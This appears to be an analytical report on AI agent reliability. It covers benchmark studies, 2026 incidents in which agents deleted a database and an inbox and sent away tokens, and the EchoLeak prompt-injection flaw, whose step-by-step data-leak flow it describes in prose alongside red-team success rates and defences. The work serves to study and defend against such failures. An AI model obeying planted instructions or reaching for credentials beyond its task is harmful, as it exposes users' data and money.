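Agents handled reworded requests worse than broken tools. On τ-bench, most of the leading models handled typos and casual phrasing well, but on GAIA several became much less accurate. A customer service agent on τ-bench has only a few valid ways to change a flight, so a slight misreading does limited damage, while an agent on GAIA has the whole web available and may start a completely different search.

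The good results for broken tools are weaker evidence than they appear. The researchers' software makes 20% of tool calls fail at first. According to their published pseudocode, it then automatically retries the call up to three times, with successive recovery chances of 30%, 50% and 70%. The agent would see a failure only if all three retries failed, which would happen in about 2% of calls (0.2 × 0.7 × 0.5 × 0.3 = 0.021). If the actual software works this way, the test mostly shows that agents can cope with rare faults.

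After each task, the team asked the agent how confident it was that it had succeeded, from 0 to 100. Average confidence has moved closer to the actual success rate in recent models, particularly Anthropic's Claude models. But it was still far too high on τ-bench, where only the newer Claude models improved, and only modestly.

Accurate average confidence also doesn't help a user find the mistakes. If an agent issues 100 refunds, gets 90 right and reports 90% confidence for each one, its confidence is accurate on average, but the user can't use it to choose which refunds to check. On τ-bench, most models' confidence was about as useful as a random guess for separating successes from failures. Only Claude Opus 4.5 and 4.7 did somewhat better. So a rule like "ask me when you're unsure" would probably miss many cases in which the user would want to be asked.

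### Wrong charges and refunds

The safety results are more encouraging. The team had GPT-4o check the τ-bench transcripts for broken rules, such as changing a booking without permission, skipping an identity check or giving in to a customer who demanded an exception. Recent models broke far fewer rules than older ones, and most violations were of low or moderate severity. The most common violation across all models was charging or refunding the wrong amount.

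These counts are only as reliable as the language model judging them, which may miss a wrong refund or flag a correct one. The team lists human checks as future work. τ-bench's own database comparison can catch a wrong amount without a judge, but it can't show whether the agent checked the customer's identity first.

The severity scores are also milder than the judge's own labels. GPT-4o's instructions describe scores from 6 to 8 out of 10 as "high" severity and give exposed personal data as an example, but the team's formula counts those scores as medium, with half the maximum weight. A leak of personal data could therefore count the same as a much less serious problem.

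Faulty tasks do not seem to explain the poor consistency. Accuracy, safety and confidence looked better on the 26 good tasks than on the original 50, but consistency did not reliably improve. On the good tasks, agents that had been right and confident no longer lost points because of a wrong answer key.

### The same steps with different details

An agent's individual tool calls can vary between runs, as can whether it finishes the task. To study the tool calls in *How Consistent Are LLM Agents?*, independent researcher Yagubyan (2026) gave six models 19 office tasks, such as finding a contact and sending an email, and ran each task ten times at temperature 1. The simulated tools always returned the same output for the same input, so any differences came from the models.

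Across runs, the agents mostly used the same tools in the same order, with an average similarity of 0.87 out of 1. The details they entered into those tools were less similar, at 0.69. The true gap is probably somewhat smaller, because when two runs used different tools at the same step, Yagubyan also counted their details as different.

Vague requests made agents vary more. For tasks such as "Help me prepare for my meetings tomorrow", the similarity of the details was 0.52, compared with 0.72 for clearer tasks. The choice of model had no statistically significant effect on this measure. A request such as "Pay this month's bills" is similarly vague.

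Yagubyan concludes that variation in the details is harmless. Task and model combinations that used similar sequences of tools across runs were correct about 90% of the time, against 61% for the rest, but the similarity of the details did not predict success. This makes sense for office tasks, where two differently worded emails can both tell Alice that the meeting has moved to 3 pm. It may not apply to payments, which none of the ten tools in the study could make. Changing the payee, amount or date in a payment request changes what happens to the money.

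Bellibatlu and colleagues found more serious variation in details when they tested agents that write medical orders in MedAgentBench, a simulated hospital system containing real patient records with identities removed. The agents were two small models that a hospital could run on its own computers. Each attempted 50 tasks five times at each of two temperatures, and the team compared the resulting orders for tests, referrals and drugs.

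| Model and temperature | Tasks with an order in at least one run | Orders differed between runs | Order missing from some runs | Different code, value or dose |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3-4B, 0.05 | 20 | 3 | 0 | 0 |
| Qwen3-4B, 0.7 | 20 | 10 | 4 | 0 |
| Llama-3.1-8B, 0.05 | 21 | 11 | 1 | 0 |
| Llama-3.1-8B, 0.7 | 43 | 43 | 26 | 28 |

Counts like these depend on the number of runs, because a task that looks stable after five runs may still vary on the sixth, so the team also compared runs in pairs. When the team raised the temperature from 0.05 to 0.7, the share of pairs with different orders rose from 8% to 29% for Qwen and from 33% to 78% for Llama.

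Missing orders were easy to overlook. In the 26 Llama tasks where some runs had an order and others did not, the agent produced no order in 72 runs, and in 61 of these it simply declared that it had finished. Ordering nothing may have been the right decision in some tasks, so not every missing order was necessarily a mistake. Other orders went to the wrong address on the hospital's server. When the researchers sent an order to that address, the server rejected it, but in MedAgentBench the agents received a message that such orders had succeeded, so they had no reason to try again.

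Pass-or-fail scores hid much of this variation. In 22 of the 43 Llama tasks at the higher temperature, the agent failed all five times but with different orders. By Rabanser's formula, each of these tasks would get a perfect score for consistency of results.

These rates are weak evidence about the agents people now use for shopping and email. The two models succeeded in only 18% to 31% of runs, and Bellibatlu and colleagues warn against applying the rates elsewhere. No agent succeeded every time at a task while changing the substance of its order. The results show that weak agents fail in inconsistent ways, but they don't establish whether stronger agents vary as much in tasks they usually get right.

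### Repeatable and correct

A perfectly repeatable agent can still be wrong. If it pays the gas bill twice whenever a reminder arrives, its consistency score will be 1. Repeatable errors are easier to catch and fix, though, because a developer who sees one can reproduce it, find the cause and check that a correction works, whereas a rare random error can easily go unnoticed in a handful of test runs.

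Repeatability also applies only to identical inputs. Thinking Machines' routines make the model give the same answer to the same text, but rewording a request can still change the answer. A deterministic agent could pay the full credit card balance whenever the user writes "pay this month's bills from my inbox", and only the minimum whenever they write "pls sort the bills in my email", which would surprise a user who meant the same thing by both.

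In everyday use, an agent rarely gets the same input twice. Even if the user repeats a request word for word, next month's inbox will contain different emails. Temperature zero is therefore more useful to a developer investigating a past mistake than to a user who wants to predict the next payment. The user would gain more by adding "pay the credit card in full" to the request.

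## A deleted database, a deleted inbox and a transfer to a stranger

In early 2026, three AI agents with permission to act on real data or money made damaging mistakes. One deleted a company's database, another deleted emails from a researcher's inbox, and a third sent a stranger tokens with a paper value of about $250,000. None of these incidents involved an attacker. Fairly ordinary controls would have limited all three losses, but most of those controls would also have made the agents slower or less useful.

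### Nine seconds at PocketOS

PocketOS makes software that car rental companies use to manage reservations, payments and vehicles. On Friday 24 April 2026, the company had an agent working on a routine task in its staging environment, a test version of the software where mistakes should not reach customers. The agent was Cursor, a coding tool, running Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6. The company's founder described what happened next in a long post on X (Crane, *An AI Agent Just Destroyed Our Production Data. It Confessed in Writing*):

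1. The agent ran into a credential mismatch in the staging environment.
2. It set out to fix this by deleting a volume, a unit of storage at Railway, the cloud company that hosts PocketOS's data.
3. It searched for a token that Railway would accept and found one in a file unrelated to its task. PocketOS had created this token to add and remove web domains.
4. It sent Railway a single command, `volumeDelete`, with the token and the volume's ID.
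5. Railway's server accepted the token and deleted the volume, which held the live database. The volume's backups disappeared with it.

The deletion took nine seconds. The next morning, people arrived to collect rental cars from businesses that no longer had any record of them.

### How much of the data came back

When Crane published his post, about 30 hours after the deletion, the newest backup he could use was three months old. PocketOS had restored that copy, and he was helping customers reconstruct later bookings from payment records, calendars and confirmation emails. Some newer customers had no accounts in the restored database, but the payment system was still billing them.

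Crane soon announced that Railway had recovered the data, so articles that leave this out overstate the loss. *'Rogue' AI agent went haywire at tech company* (Leib, 2026) dates the announcement to Sunday, and *An AI agent deleted a company's entire database in 9 seconds* (Farrant) dates it to Monday. Railway says that the customer has "all their data", and Tom's Hardware's *Victim of AI agent that deleted company's entire database gets their data* (2026) describes the recovery as apparently complete. These claims rest on the word of the two companies, but their accounts agree, even though Crane had been criticising Railway harshly until then.

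Crane and Railway's chief executive both say that the restoration took 30 minutes, counting from when they made direct contact. Crane had appealed to the chief executive publicly within ten minutes of the deletion, so most of the outage seems to have been spent reaching someone who could help and establishing that a copy existed.

PocketOS was also fortunate that Railway had that copy. Eleven days earlier, another customer had lost a volume through the same command. In the support thread, *Postgress volume lost* (2026), a Railway employee explained that the deletion was immediate and permanent, as the documentation stated. The copies that saved PocketOS were "disaster backups", which Railway keeps at another site in case of hardware failure or natural disaster. O'Reilly's *When an Agent Deletes the Production Database* argues that after a deletion with a valid credential, the largest cloud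 companies would have had no copy of the data unless the customer had made its own backups.

### A rule in the prompt and a key in a file

PocketOS had given its agent written safety rules, and Cursor had added some of its own. The agent later quoted a rule that prohibited destructive or irreversible git commands unless the user explicitly requested them.

These rules, like Robb's order to Muse not to agree to another pickup, were only text in the context window. They made a destructive command less likely but didn't block it. Railway's server received just a valid token and a command, and it handled them as it would a request from any other program.

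The rule's wording may also have mattered. Git is a tool for tracking versions of code, and a request to delete a storage volume is not a git command. A careful engineer would see that the reason for the rule applies even more strongly to a database. A model may make the same inference on most runs but not all. It also has to recognise that an action is destructive, and deleting a volume can look like routine cleaning up if the model thinks the volume is part of a disposable test system.

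Even a rule that nearly always works can be inadequate for an agent that runs all day. Suppose an agent faces ten situations a day in which a destructive command looks like a convenient fix, and the rule stops it 99.9% of the time. The agent would still run such a command about once every 100 days.

Crane concludes that instructions to a model are "advisory, not enforcing", and that the services an agent connects to have to enforce the limits. He also blames Cursor, whose documentation describes guardrails that can stop commands from destroying live systems. It is unclear why they didn't stop this one. They may have missed it because the agent used curl, an ordinary program for sending web requests, and the destructive part was inside the request. Tom's Hardware had seen no public explanation from Cursor or Anthropic when it reported the recovery.

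### What the confession can show

When Crane asked the agent why it had made the deletion, it replied that it had guessed only staging would be affected and had not checked. It also said, "I violated every principle I was given". Crane presented this as the agent admitting on the record which rules it had ignored, and the reply made headlines around the world.

Like Muse's explanation of its false reply to Robb's buyer, this apology is generated text and weak evidence about why the database was deleted. The model now had in its context the safety rules, the deletion command and a question from a user whose database was gone. An apology that goes through the rules one by one is a likely continuation of that text, whatever led to the deletion. Live Science's *I violated every principle I was given* makes a similar point and adds that agents can be sycophantic towards their users.

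Two different causes could lead the model to write the same confession. It might have wrongly inferred that the volume belonged only to staging. Or it might never have worked out which environment the volume belonged to, and followed the common programming pattern of deleting a misconfigured resource and creating it again.

Some of the agent's statements can be checked, though. It said it had not read Railway's documentation, and a log of its tool calls would show whether it opened those pages. The log may also contain text the model wrote before the deletion. That text would be better evidence than a later explanation, although it too can leave out what influenced the model's choice. Crane has since gone through the session log and the project rules on camera, according to ServiceNow's *Learnings from when an AI agent goes rogue*.

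The apology is also weak evidence of how the agent will behave in its next run. O'Reilly contrasts the agent with a person who has helped cause a major outage and remembers the dread for years. A new session with the same model starts with no memory of the PocketOS incident unless someone adds a description of it to the context window.

### Narrower keys, slower deletion, separate backups

The token that PocketOS had made for managing domains could also delete a database. Crane complained that every Railway token was effectively all-powerful. Railway's Abdelwahab disagrees in *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*. He says customers could limit a token to one workspace or one project, but PocketOS's token covered the whole account. He concedes that the process for creating a token did not make the choice obvious.

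The Daily WTF's *Empty Pockets* helps reconcile the two accounts. Railway's narrowest tokens were limited to one environment but could do anything within it. A token restricted to staging would have prevented the loss, but it could not have managed the live service's domains. That required a token for the live environment, which could also have deleted the live database. PocketOS needed a token limited to one type of action, changing domains.

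This is the principle of least privilege, which means giving each person or program only the access its job requires. Applying it takes time, because someone has to work out what each job requires and create a separate key for it. It also makes an agent less able to handle surprises. If an agent working overnight needs another permission, it stops, and its user finds the task unfinished in the morning.

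A key limited to the agent's own task would not have been enough, because this agent went looking for a different one. The O'Reilly article mentions that the same thing recently happened to one of its author's clients. So the other keys have to be out of reach too. Tokens can expire after an hour, so a leftover one no longer works when an agent finds it. The agent can also run in a sandbox, a closed environment where it sees only some of the user's files. But if tokens expire, a script that updates domains every night needs a way to get a new one, and an agent that sees fewer files can fix fewer problems.

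Delayed deletion would have protected the data even though the wrong key was used, because PocketOS could have undone the deletion within minutes of noticing it. Railway already had a delay for people who clicked "delete" on its website. As Abdelwahab had explained in an earlier post, the software schedules the volume for removal, and the user has 48 hours to change their mind. Commands sent directly by other programs skipped the delay until Railway changed its system after the incident.

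The delay barely slows a competent agent, which can keep working while the old volume is retained. The customer may have to pay for storage longer, and private data that someone meant to erase remains for two more days. A company that creates and deletes 100 test databases a day would have about 200 awaiting permanent deletion at any time. The delay can also end before anyone notices the deletion. The one on Friday afternoon would have become final on Sunday afternoon if nobody had noticed it.

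Crane wants a stricter safeguard, a confirmation that an agent cannot complete by itself, such as a text message to the owner. The O'Reilly article objects that these interfaces exist to let programs work without people, and that customers who want a human check have to build one themselves. A delay avoids much of this conflict because a person can still intervene, but programs don't have to wait for approval.

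Separate backups would have reduced the damage with the least effect on what the agent could do. If the newest separate copy is from last night, a company loses at most a day of data. Without Railway's disaster backups, PocketOS would have lost three months of data. But a copy on another disk is not necessarily separate. For George Gerchow, a security specialist quoted in IANS's *I Violated Every Principle* (2026), the scariest detail is that the interface the agent used to delete the database also held the backups. A useful backup therefore needs its own credential, stored where the agent cannot find it. The company must also pay for storage and regular restore tests, and protect one more set of customer records from leaks.

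### How an inbox agent lost its instruction

Summer Yue, director of alignment at Meta Superintelligence Labs, works on making AI systems do what people intend. In February 2026, she was using OpenClaw, the open-source agent on which Meta later modelled Muse, to sort her email. She asked it to suggest what to archive or delete, and added "don't action until I tell you to". Fortune (2026) reports that this had worked for weeks in a test inbox.

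Then she connected her real inbox, and the agent began deleting emails. Willison describes screenshots in which she tries to stop it from her phone. At 6:00 pm she asked it what it was doing. She wrote "Do not do that" at 6:01, told it to stop at 6:02, and wrote "STOP OPENCLAW" at 6:03. The agent continued, and a note in one of its commands read "Keep looping until we clear everything old". Yue ran to the Mac mini that hosted it and shut the agent down there.

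Accounts of the damage differ. TechBriefly's *OpenClaw AI agent ignores instructions wipes 200 emails for Meta director* (2026) reports more than 200 deleted emails, whereas Fortune reports that the agent deleted the entire inbox. HackerNoon's *Your Agent Doesn't Need to Be Malicious to Ruin Your Day* says the agent "bulk-trashed" hundreds. If the emails only went to the trash folder, Yue could probably have restored them.

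Yue says that her real inbox was so large that it triggered compaction, and that the agent lost her original instruction in the process. Compaction lets an agent continue a task that has outgrown its context window. When the text approaches the limit, the program has a model summarise the older part and replaces that part with the summary.

A short instruction can disappear when the program summarises a long context. Suppose the context window holds 200,000 tokens and an average email is 500 tokens. A test inbox of 50 emails uses 25,000 tokens, so the program never needs to summarise anything. In a real inbox, the window fills up after about 400 emails. Yue's request is then perhaps 25 tokens out of 200,000, and the summary has to be many times shorter than the original. A summary such as "the user wants to clear old mail from this inbox" would be reasonable for most purposes, but it keeps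 the goal and drops the condition, so an agent that reads it has no reason to wait.

A long task may require several compactions. If each summary has a 95% chance of preserving the instruction, the instruction has only about a 60% chance of surviving ten of them (0.95^10 ≈ 0.60). A test inbox that never triggers compaction carries no such risk, however many weeks the test lasts. Yue's successful trial was therefore good evidence about small inboxes but almost none about large ones, and she called relying on it a "rookie mistake".

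Her account fits the way compaction works, but nobody seems to have confirmed it independently. CoClaw, an unofficial site about the software, notes that the product's documentation and code do not prove that compaction caused the loss. Yue wasn't certain of the whole explanation either. When someone suggested that other instructions might have told her agent to be proactive, she replied that she had deleted all the ones she could find but might have missed one, according to Windows Central's *Meta's safety director handed OpenClaw AI agents the keys to her emails*.

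Compaction also doesn't explain why the agent carried on after she told it to stop. Those messages were new, so summarizing the older history should not have removed them. The program may have held them back until the agent finished its current series of actions, or the model may have read them and continued anyway, but the screenshots don't show which.

If Yue is right, her original instruction was no longer in the model's input. A model better at following instructions would not have prevented that part of the failure, although it might have stopped when she told it to. Many reports, including the AI-generated summary in OECD's *Meta AI Director's Emails Deleted by Rogue OpenClaw AI Agent* (2026), say instead that the agent ignored her instruction.

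### Keeping the limit outside the conversation

The simplest fix is to have the program store important instructions separately and add them back after every compaction. This uses a little of the context window, and someone has to decide which instructions are important. The fix would have addressed the cause Yue identified. But the instruction would still be text, which an agent might not follow. PocketOS's agent deleted a volume even though its rules were in its context window.

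A login that could read emails but not delete them would have prevented the loss, whatever the model remembered. The agent could still have listed its suggestions, as Yue had asked, but she would have had to delete the emails herself. That seems a minor inconvenience for a first run on a large inbox, though it removes most of the benefit for someone with 10,000 old newsletters.

A compromise is to let the agent move emails to a folder but not delete them permanently. Yue could then have reviewed the folder and moved back anything she wanted to keep. The emails would still take up storage until she emptied the folder, and keeping them would be a privacy risk if she wanted any gone because of what they contained.

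The mail software could also limit the number of deletions. With a cap of 20 an hour, the agent could have deleted at most 20 emails before Yue reached her computer, unless a new hour had begun. But clearing 5,000 emails at that rate would take 250 hours. Requiring approval after the first 20 would be more practical, since the user could by then see whether the agent was choosing sensibly. Ordinary software has to keep the count, because a count in the context window could disappear the same way the instruction did.

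Yue also needed a stop button that worked from her phone. A button that ends the process or revokes the login works even if the program fails to deliver a message asking the agent to stop, or the model ignores it. But it may interrupt a task halfway, leaving some emails moved and others not. That is easy to sort out in an inbox, but it could cause trouble in a series of linked payments.

### Lobstar Wilde's missing balance

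In February 2026, a cryptocurrency-trading agent called Lobstar Wilde sent a stranger tokens nominally worth about $250,000. It had lost the record of its own holdings, much as Yue's agent had lost an instruction. The tokens were units of a digital currency, not the units of text that a language model reads.

A trading agent can calculate its balance from the purchases and sales recorded in its context window, or it can query the blockchain, the shared ledger that determines who owns what. The two balances match only while the agent's record is complete, and a compaction or restart can erase part of that record without changing the ledger.

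Suppose an agent holds 50 million tokens, but its surviving notes record only the 50,000 it bought this morning. It agrees to give someone its whole balance, which is a small gift according to the notes. The wallet software looks up the true balance and sends all 50 million. Every part of the system has followed its instructions, and no one can reverse the transfer without the recipient's cooperation.

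Reading the balance from the ledger immediately before each transfer would remove this discrepancy, and usually adds only a short delay and one more tool call. But an agent that knows its exact balance can still send far too much of it by misplacing a decimal point or being too generous.

A transfer cap would also limit losses from those errors. If the wallet software had refused to send more than $500 to a new recipient, a single transfer could have cost at most 0.2% of the $250,000. A daily cap is also needed, because otherwise an agent could repeat the mistake 500 times. The software has to enforce both caps itself. Signed spending limits are a more elaborate version of the same idea.

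Caps are awkward for traders, who may need to move large amounts quickly. The owner could exempt transfers to a few known exchanges and cap all others, which would leave most trading unaffected. The agent would then need its owner's help to make a large legitimate payment to someone new. Alternatively, such payments could be held for an hour so that the owner can cancel them, but the price may change in that time, and the owner may be asleep and miss the chance to cancel.

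The $250,000 is also a paper value, which is the number of tokens multiplied by the latest price. That price may apply only to small sales. Many small cryptocurrencies trade through automated pools that contain both the token and dollars (or something easily exchanged for dollars). In the most common design, the number of tokens multiplied by the number of dollars stays constant, so each token sold lowers the price of the next. If someone sells tokens with a paper value of V to a pool containing D dollars, they receive

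V / (1 + V/D)

before fees. The sale also divides the market price by (1 + V/D)². These are illustrative results for a paper value of $250,000:

| Dollars in the pool | What the seller receives | Price after the sale, compared with before |
|---|---|---|
| $5,000,000 | about $238,000 | 91% |
| $250,000 | $125,000 | 25% |
| $50,000 | about $41,700 | 3% |

With a small pool, the recipient gets far less than $250,000 for the tokens. The owner could not have sold them for that much either, so the owner loses less than $250,000 in spendable money. But everyone else who holds the token loses when the price collapses, even though they never gave the agent access to anything.

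## EchoLeak, an email that could make an office assistant leak data

EchoLeak was a flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot, the AI assistant in Microsoft's office software. An outsider could send an employee a single email and get Copilot to collect private company data and pass it on. Unlike the deletions at PocketOS and in Summer Yue's inbox, EchoLeak required an attacker, who would use prompt injection to give Copilot instructions.

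### One stream of text

When a user asks an assistant to summarise an email, the program joins the developer's rules, the user's request and the email into one sequence of tokens. Willison (2025) argues in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* that this is why models can't reliably treat instructions differently depending on where they came from.

Programs put markers around the user's request and around the results of tool calls, and developers train models to give the user's words more weight. But the markers are part of the same sequence as the text they label. Training makes a model less likely to follow an instruction inside an email, but doesn't make it impossible.

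Willison named prompt injection after SQL injection, an older attack in which someone types database commands into a form on a website. Programmers can prevent SQL injection by sending the command and the form's contents to the database separately, so that the database never runs the contents as a command. They can't do the same with a language model, because it has no separate input for commands.

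Telling the model to disregard everything in an email wouldn't work either, because users want agents to act on what their emails contain. To pay a gas bill, the agent has to take the amount and the due date from a message that someone else wrote. Reflection, an AI company, tries to address this with a short written policy for its agent, which *Beam Model Technical Report* (2026) reproduces. The policy lets retrieved text supply values for the next step of the user's task, but not instructions about what to do next. Like the safety rules at PocketOS, this policy is text that the model may fail to apply. It also doesn't protect against a forged bill, because the account number on the bill is a value, which the policy allows the agent to use.

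### How the data could get out

*EchoLeak* and later analyses describe the same flow of data:

1. The attacker sends an employee an email containing text meant for the assistant.
2. The employee later asks Copilot a work question. Copilot searches the employee's emails and files for relevant material, and the attacker's email is among the results.
3. The email and the company's private documents are now in the same context window. The model follows the planted instruction and picks out sensitive data.
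4. Copilot's answer includes a web address with that data written into it.
5. The software loads the address automatically, which delivers the data to the attacker's server.

The employee doesn't have to open the email or click on anything, so security researchers call this a zero-click attack. An earlier Copilot flaw, which Microsoft fixed in July 2024, required the user to click a link, according to *Trust No AI* (2024).

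Access permissions did not help, because the employee was allowed to see every document that Copilot read. Microsoft had other defences: a filter to detect injected instructions, a step that removed outside links, and a list of approved sites from which Copilot could load content. *EchoLeak* (2025) explains that the attack got past all three. A Microsoft service on the approved list relayed the final request.

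Aim Labs, the research group that found the flaw, reported it to Microsoft in January 2025. Microsoft fixed it on its own servers in May, according to Information Security Buzz, so customers didn't have to install anything. Microsoft published an advisory on 11 June under the identifier CVE-2025-32711. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) reports that Microsoft rated the flaw 9.3 out of 10 (critical), while the US National Vulnerability Database rated it 7.5 (high).

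Microsoft said that nobody had exploited the flaw outside research, according to SC Media's *Microsoft 365 Copilot ‘zero-click’ vulnerability enabled data exfiltration*. Customers may find it hard to check such statements. In ShadowLeak, a similar flaw in a ChatGPT research agent connected to Gmail, the request carrying the data was sent from the provider's servers, so the victim's monitoring software could have missed it. There is no evidence that criminals used ShadowLeak either.

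Attackers appear to be using prompt injection now. Adrien Merveille of the security firm Check Point described one case to the French technology site Clubic. A company used agents to review its security logs, and intruders put an instruction in a part of their web requests that the logs recorded. According to Clubic's *Une phrase cachée dans un mail suffit à manipuler une IA*, an agent obeyed and stopped recording their activity. The account is second-hand, and the company is not named.

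Ox Security examined 542,207 open-source software components between July and October 2026. Of the agent skills (packaged instructions for particular tasks) that it flagged as suspicious, 44% directed agents to send data out, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Researchers Find a New AI Attack Path*. This percentage covers only flagged skills, so it doesn't show how common malicious skills are.

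### Three conditions for a leak

An agent can leak data this way only if it can access private data, reads text that an attacker could have written, and can send information out. Willison calls this combination the "lethal trifecta". Removing any one of the three would have stopped EchoLeak, but each makes an assistant useful.

| What the agent loses | Why the leak fails | What the user gives up |
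|---|---|---|
| Access to private data | The planted instruction finds nothing worth stealing | Answers based on the user's own contracts, messages and accounts |
| Exposure to untrusted text | The instruction never reaches the model | Help with email from outside, web pages and shared files |
| Any way to send information out | The data stays in the conversation | Sending replies, looking things up online, making payments, and perhaps links and images in answers |

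For an office assistant that mainly answers questions, removing its ability to send data out is often the least disruptive fix. Willison says that vendors have fixed most such flaws this way. Amazon, for example, stopped its business assistant from displaying clickable links. The model is still just as likely to follow a planted instruction, though, so another route for sending data out may work just as well if someone finds one.

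An agent that runs errands can leak data through many routes. An email, a web form or the reference number on a bank transfer can each carry a stolen password. Requiring the user to approve each outgoing message only partly closes these routes, because the user has to notice the data in the message.

The user can also separate the three by task. One session might read outside email with no access to anything else, while another searches private files with no access to the web. But if the first session writes a summary for the second, the summary could include a planted instruction. CaMeL takes this separation further by keeping untrusted text from choosing actions.

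Stealing money requires fewer conditions than leaking data. An agent that reads outside email and can pay new recipients meets only two of the conditions in any meaningful sense, but an attacker doesn't need to see private documents to get a transfer or to make the agent delete files. People can also ask an agent for secrets directly instead of planting text, as they did in Agents of Chaos, a two-week test of agents with their own email accounts.

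### How resistant models are now

Injection test results depend heavily on who is attacking. In the simplest tests, researchers plant a fixed message and count how often agents obey it. Reflection tested eleven open-weight models this way, using a single request to do the attacker's task first, written as if it came from the user. It ran the test on each model 949 times with one set of tasks and 560 times with another. Without a written policy against injections, the attack's success rate ranged from zero for DeepSeek V4.1 Flash to about 45% for Inkling 1T on the second set. The rates for Reflection's own model, Beam, were 3.1% and 3.6% on the two sets.

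Adding the policy, a single paragraph of text, reduced Beam's rates to 0.3% and zero, and Inkling's to 1.1% and 4.6%. The share of ordinary tasks the agents completed rose or fell by only a few percentage points.

But a real attacker can rewrite a message that fails and try again. Reflection also commissioned tests from Gray Swan, a security firm. Its attacking software, Shade, makes up to 200 attempts in each scenario and adapts as it goes. Individual attempts on Beam rarely succeeded, but in most scenarios at least one did.

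Anthropic tested Claude Opus 5, which it released in July 2026, with the same software and ran a separate browser test using attacks by professional testers. The results below come from Anthropic's system card (the report a developer publishes on a model's tests) and are for the model with extended thinking on. A scenario counts as breached if at least one attempt succeeded.

| Setting | Attempts per scenario | No added safeguards | With safeguards |
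|---|---|---|---|
| Writing code | 200 | 0.56% of attempts, 13 of 40 scenarios breached | 0.18%, 4 of 40 |
| Operating a computer through its screen | 200 | 0.54%, 1 of 14 | 0.25%, 1 of 14 |
| Browsing the web | 10 | 3.70%, 11 of 129 | 0%, 0 of 129 |

In the first two rows, the safeguards are probes that check tool results for planted instructions before the model acts on them. The browser test used auto mode, which adds a second model that blocks dangerous tool calls. In the coding test, the attacking software had practised on earlier models, so one that had practised on Opus 5 might do better.

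Progress has been quick. Attacks on Opus 4.8, the previous model in the same line, succeeded in 31.5% of browser attempts without safeguards. But a more capable model isn't always more resistant. In the same test, Claude Mythos 5 failed 29.7% of the time, while the smaller Claude Sonnet 5 failed 0.93%.

Anthropic also compared models from several companies using 1,130 attacks that people found in a Gray Swan competition. An attacker with 15 attempts had a 2.0% chance of success against Opus 5, 16.5% against Meta's Muse Spark and 20.0% against OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol. Anthropic selected and reported this comparison itself. However, it tested its own models without extra safeguards, and the other companies' models may have had some.

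The most independent figures come from an earlier round of that competition, which tested older models. According to *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (2026), 464 people made 272,000 attempts against 13 models and succeeded 8,648 times, or about 3% of the time. Claude Opus 4.5 had the lowest rate, at 0.5%, and Gemini 2.5 Pro the highest, at 8.5%. *INFUSE* (2026) tested models ranging from old, small ones to GPT-5.4 on 40 tasks and found that 19.6% of attacks succeeded on average. Attacks also made agents worse at the user's own task. For example, GPT-4o-mini's success rate fell from 77.5% to 62.6%.

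### What repeated attempts do to a low rate

If each attempt succeeds with probability q, and attempts are independent, the chance that at least one of n attempts succeeds is

1 − (1 − q)^n.

If each attempt has a 1% chance of success (q = 1%), an attacker has about a 10% chance of succeeding at least once in ten attempts, 63% in 100 and more than 99% in 500. Emails cost almost nothing to send, so a defence that stops 99% of attempts may not hold for long against someone who keeps trying.

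Real attempts aren't independent, because some situations are much easier to attack than others. Gray Swan measured a 4.7% success rate for one strong attack on Claude Opus 4.5, rising to 33.6% with ten attempts and 63% with 100, according to The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*. If the attempts were independent, the rate would have been 38% with ten and 99% with 100. The formula therefore overstates how often repeated attacks succeed on average.

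The average success rate also hides differences between scenarios. When Opus 5 operated a computer without added safeguards, 0.54% of 2,800 attack attempts succeeded, or about 15. All of them came from one of the fourteen scenarios, where the attacker had 200 attempts and succeeded about 7.5% of the time. The average therefore understates the risk for a user whose work resembles that scenario.

An attacker can also send one message to many people. If 10,000 agents read it and each has a 1% chance of obeying, the expected number of successes is 100, whether or not the outcomes are independent. Users of the same product run the same model, so the actual number may be close to zero for most messages and in the thousands for a few.

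Anthropic points out that its tests favour attackers, because real ones don't know exactly how their target has set up the agent and are more likely to get caught the more they try. That is probably true of attacks on one company's custom system. It is less reassuring for a consumer product, because a criminal can buy a subscription, practise on their own account and send victims only the message that works.

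### Is a low rate low enough for payments?

Some of the evidence supports relying on better models and filters. The Decoder's headline, *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*, reflects the zero success rate for attacks in Anthropic's browser test. Anthropic has since made auto mode the default in its coding agent on several paid plans, which Willison takes as a sign of real confidence in his collection *30 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”*. A payment system also doesn't need to stop every attack. People fall for forged invoices too, and businesses accept some fraud because checking everything would cost more.

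An attack that looks like ordinary business could get past both of auto mode's filters, the one that inspects incoming text and the one that inspects outgoing actions. A forged gas bill looks like a real one when it arrives, and paying it looks like a normal payment. If each filter missed 5% of attacks independently, only 0.25% would get past both, but attacks like this could make the share higher.

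Finding no breaches in 129 scenarios also doesn't rule out successful attacks. Even if the scenarios were a random sample of the situations users face, the result would be consistent, at the usual 95% level, with an attacker being able to breach about 2.3% of those situations. The scenarios aren't a random sample, and attackers will look for situations the testers didn't think of.

Willison distrusts products that claim to catch 95% of attacks, because he considers that a failing grade in web security. OpenAI conceded in December 2025 that prompt injection may never be fully solved, according to The Decoder. Attackers have weakened many published defences by adapting to them. *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection* (Zorz, 2026) describes research in which training on more attacks left agents easier to hijack, as a large collection may mostly repeat the same attack.

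The alternative is to restrict what the agent can do with ordinary software that applies the same rules however persuasive the email is. Microsoft has developed FIDES, which uses fixed rules to control where information may flow, according to PYMNTS's *Anthropic Pushes Back as Hackers Press AI Weak Spots*. But fixed rules stop only what they cover. A spending limit won't stop a forged bill below the limit, and a list of approved payees won't help if the user adds the criminal to it.

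For payments, the choice depends on how much money one successful attack can take. Suppose an agent reads 50 malicious emails a year and each has a 0.2% chance of working, which is Opus 5's rate for a single attempt in the comparison between companies. That is one success every ten years on average. If the attacker takes all $40,000 in savings that the login can reach, the expected loss is $4,000 a year. A model ten times as resistant would reduce this to $400. If the bank instead refused to send more than $150 in total to new payees until the user had reviewed the account, the expected loss would be $15 a year with the original model.

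A limit set outside the model protects the user more here than a large improvement in the model would, and a user can have both. Private data has no equivalent of a $150 limit. An agent that can read a whole inbox can leak its most sensitive email on the first successful attempt, and the only way to limit that loss is to deny the agent access to that email.

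## CaMeL, a design that keeps untrusted text from choosing actions

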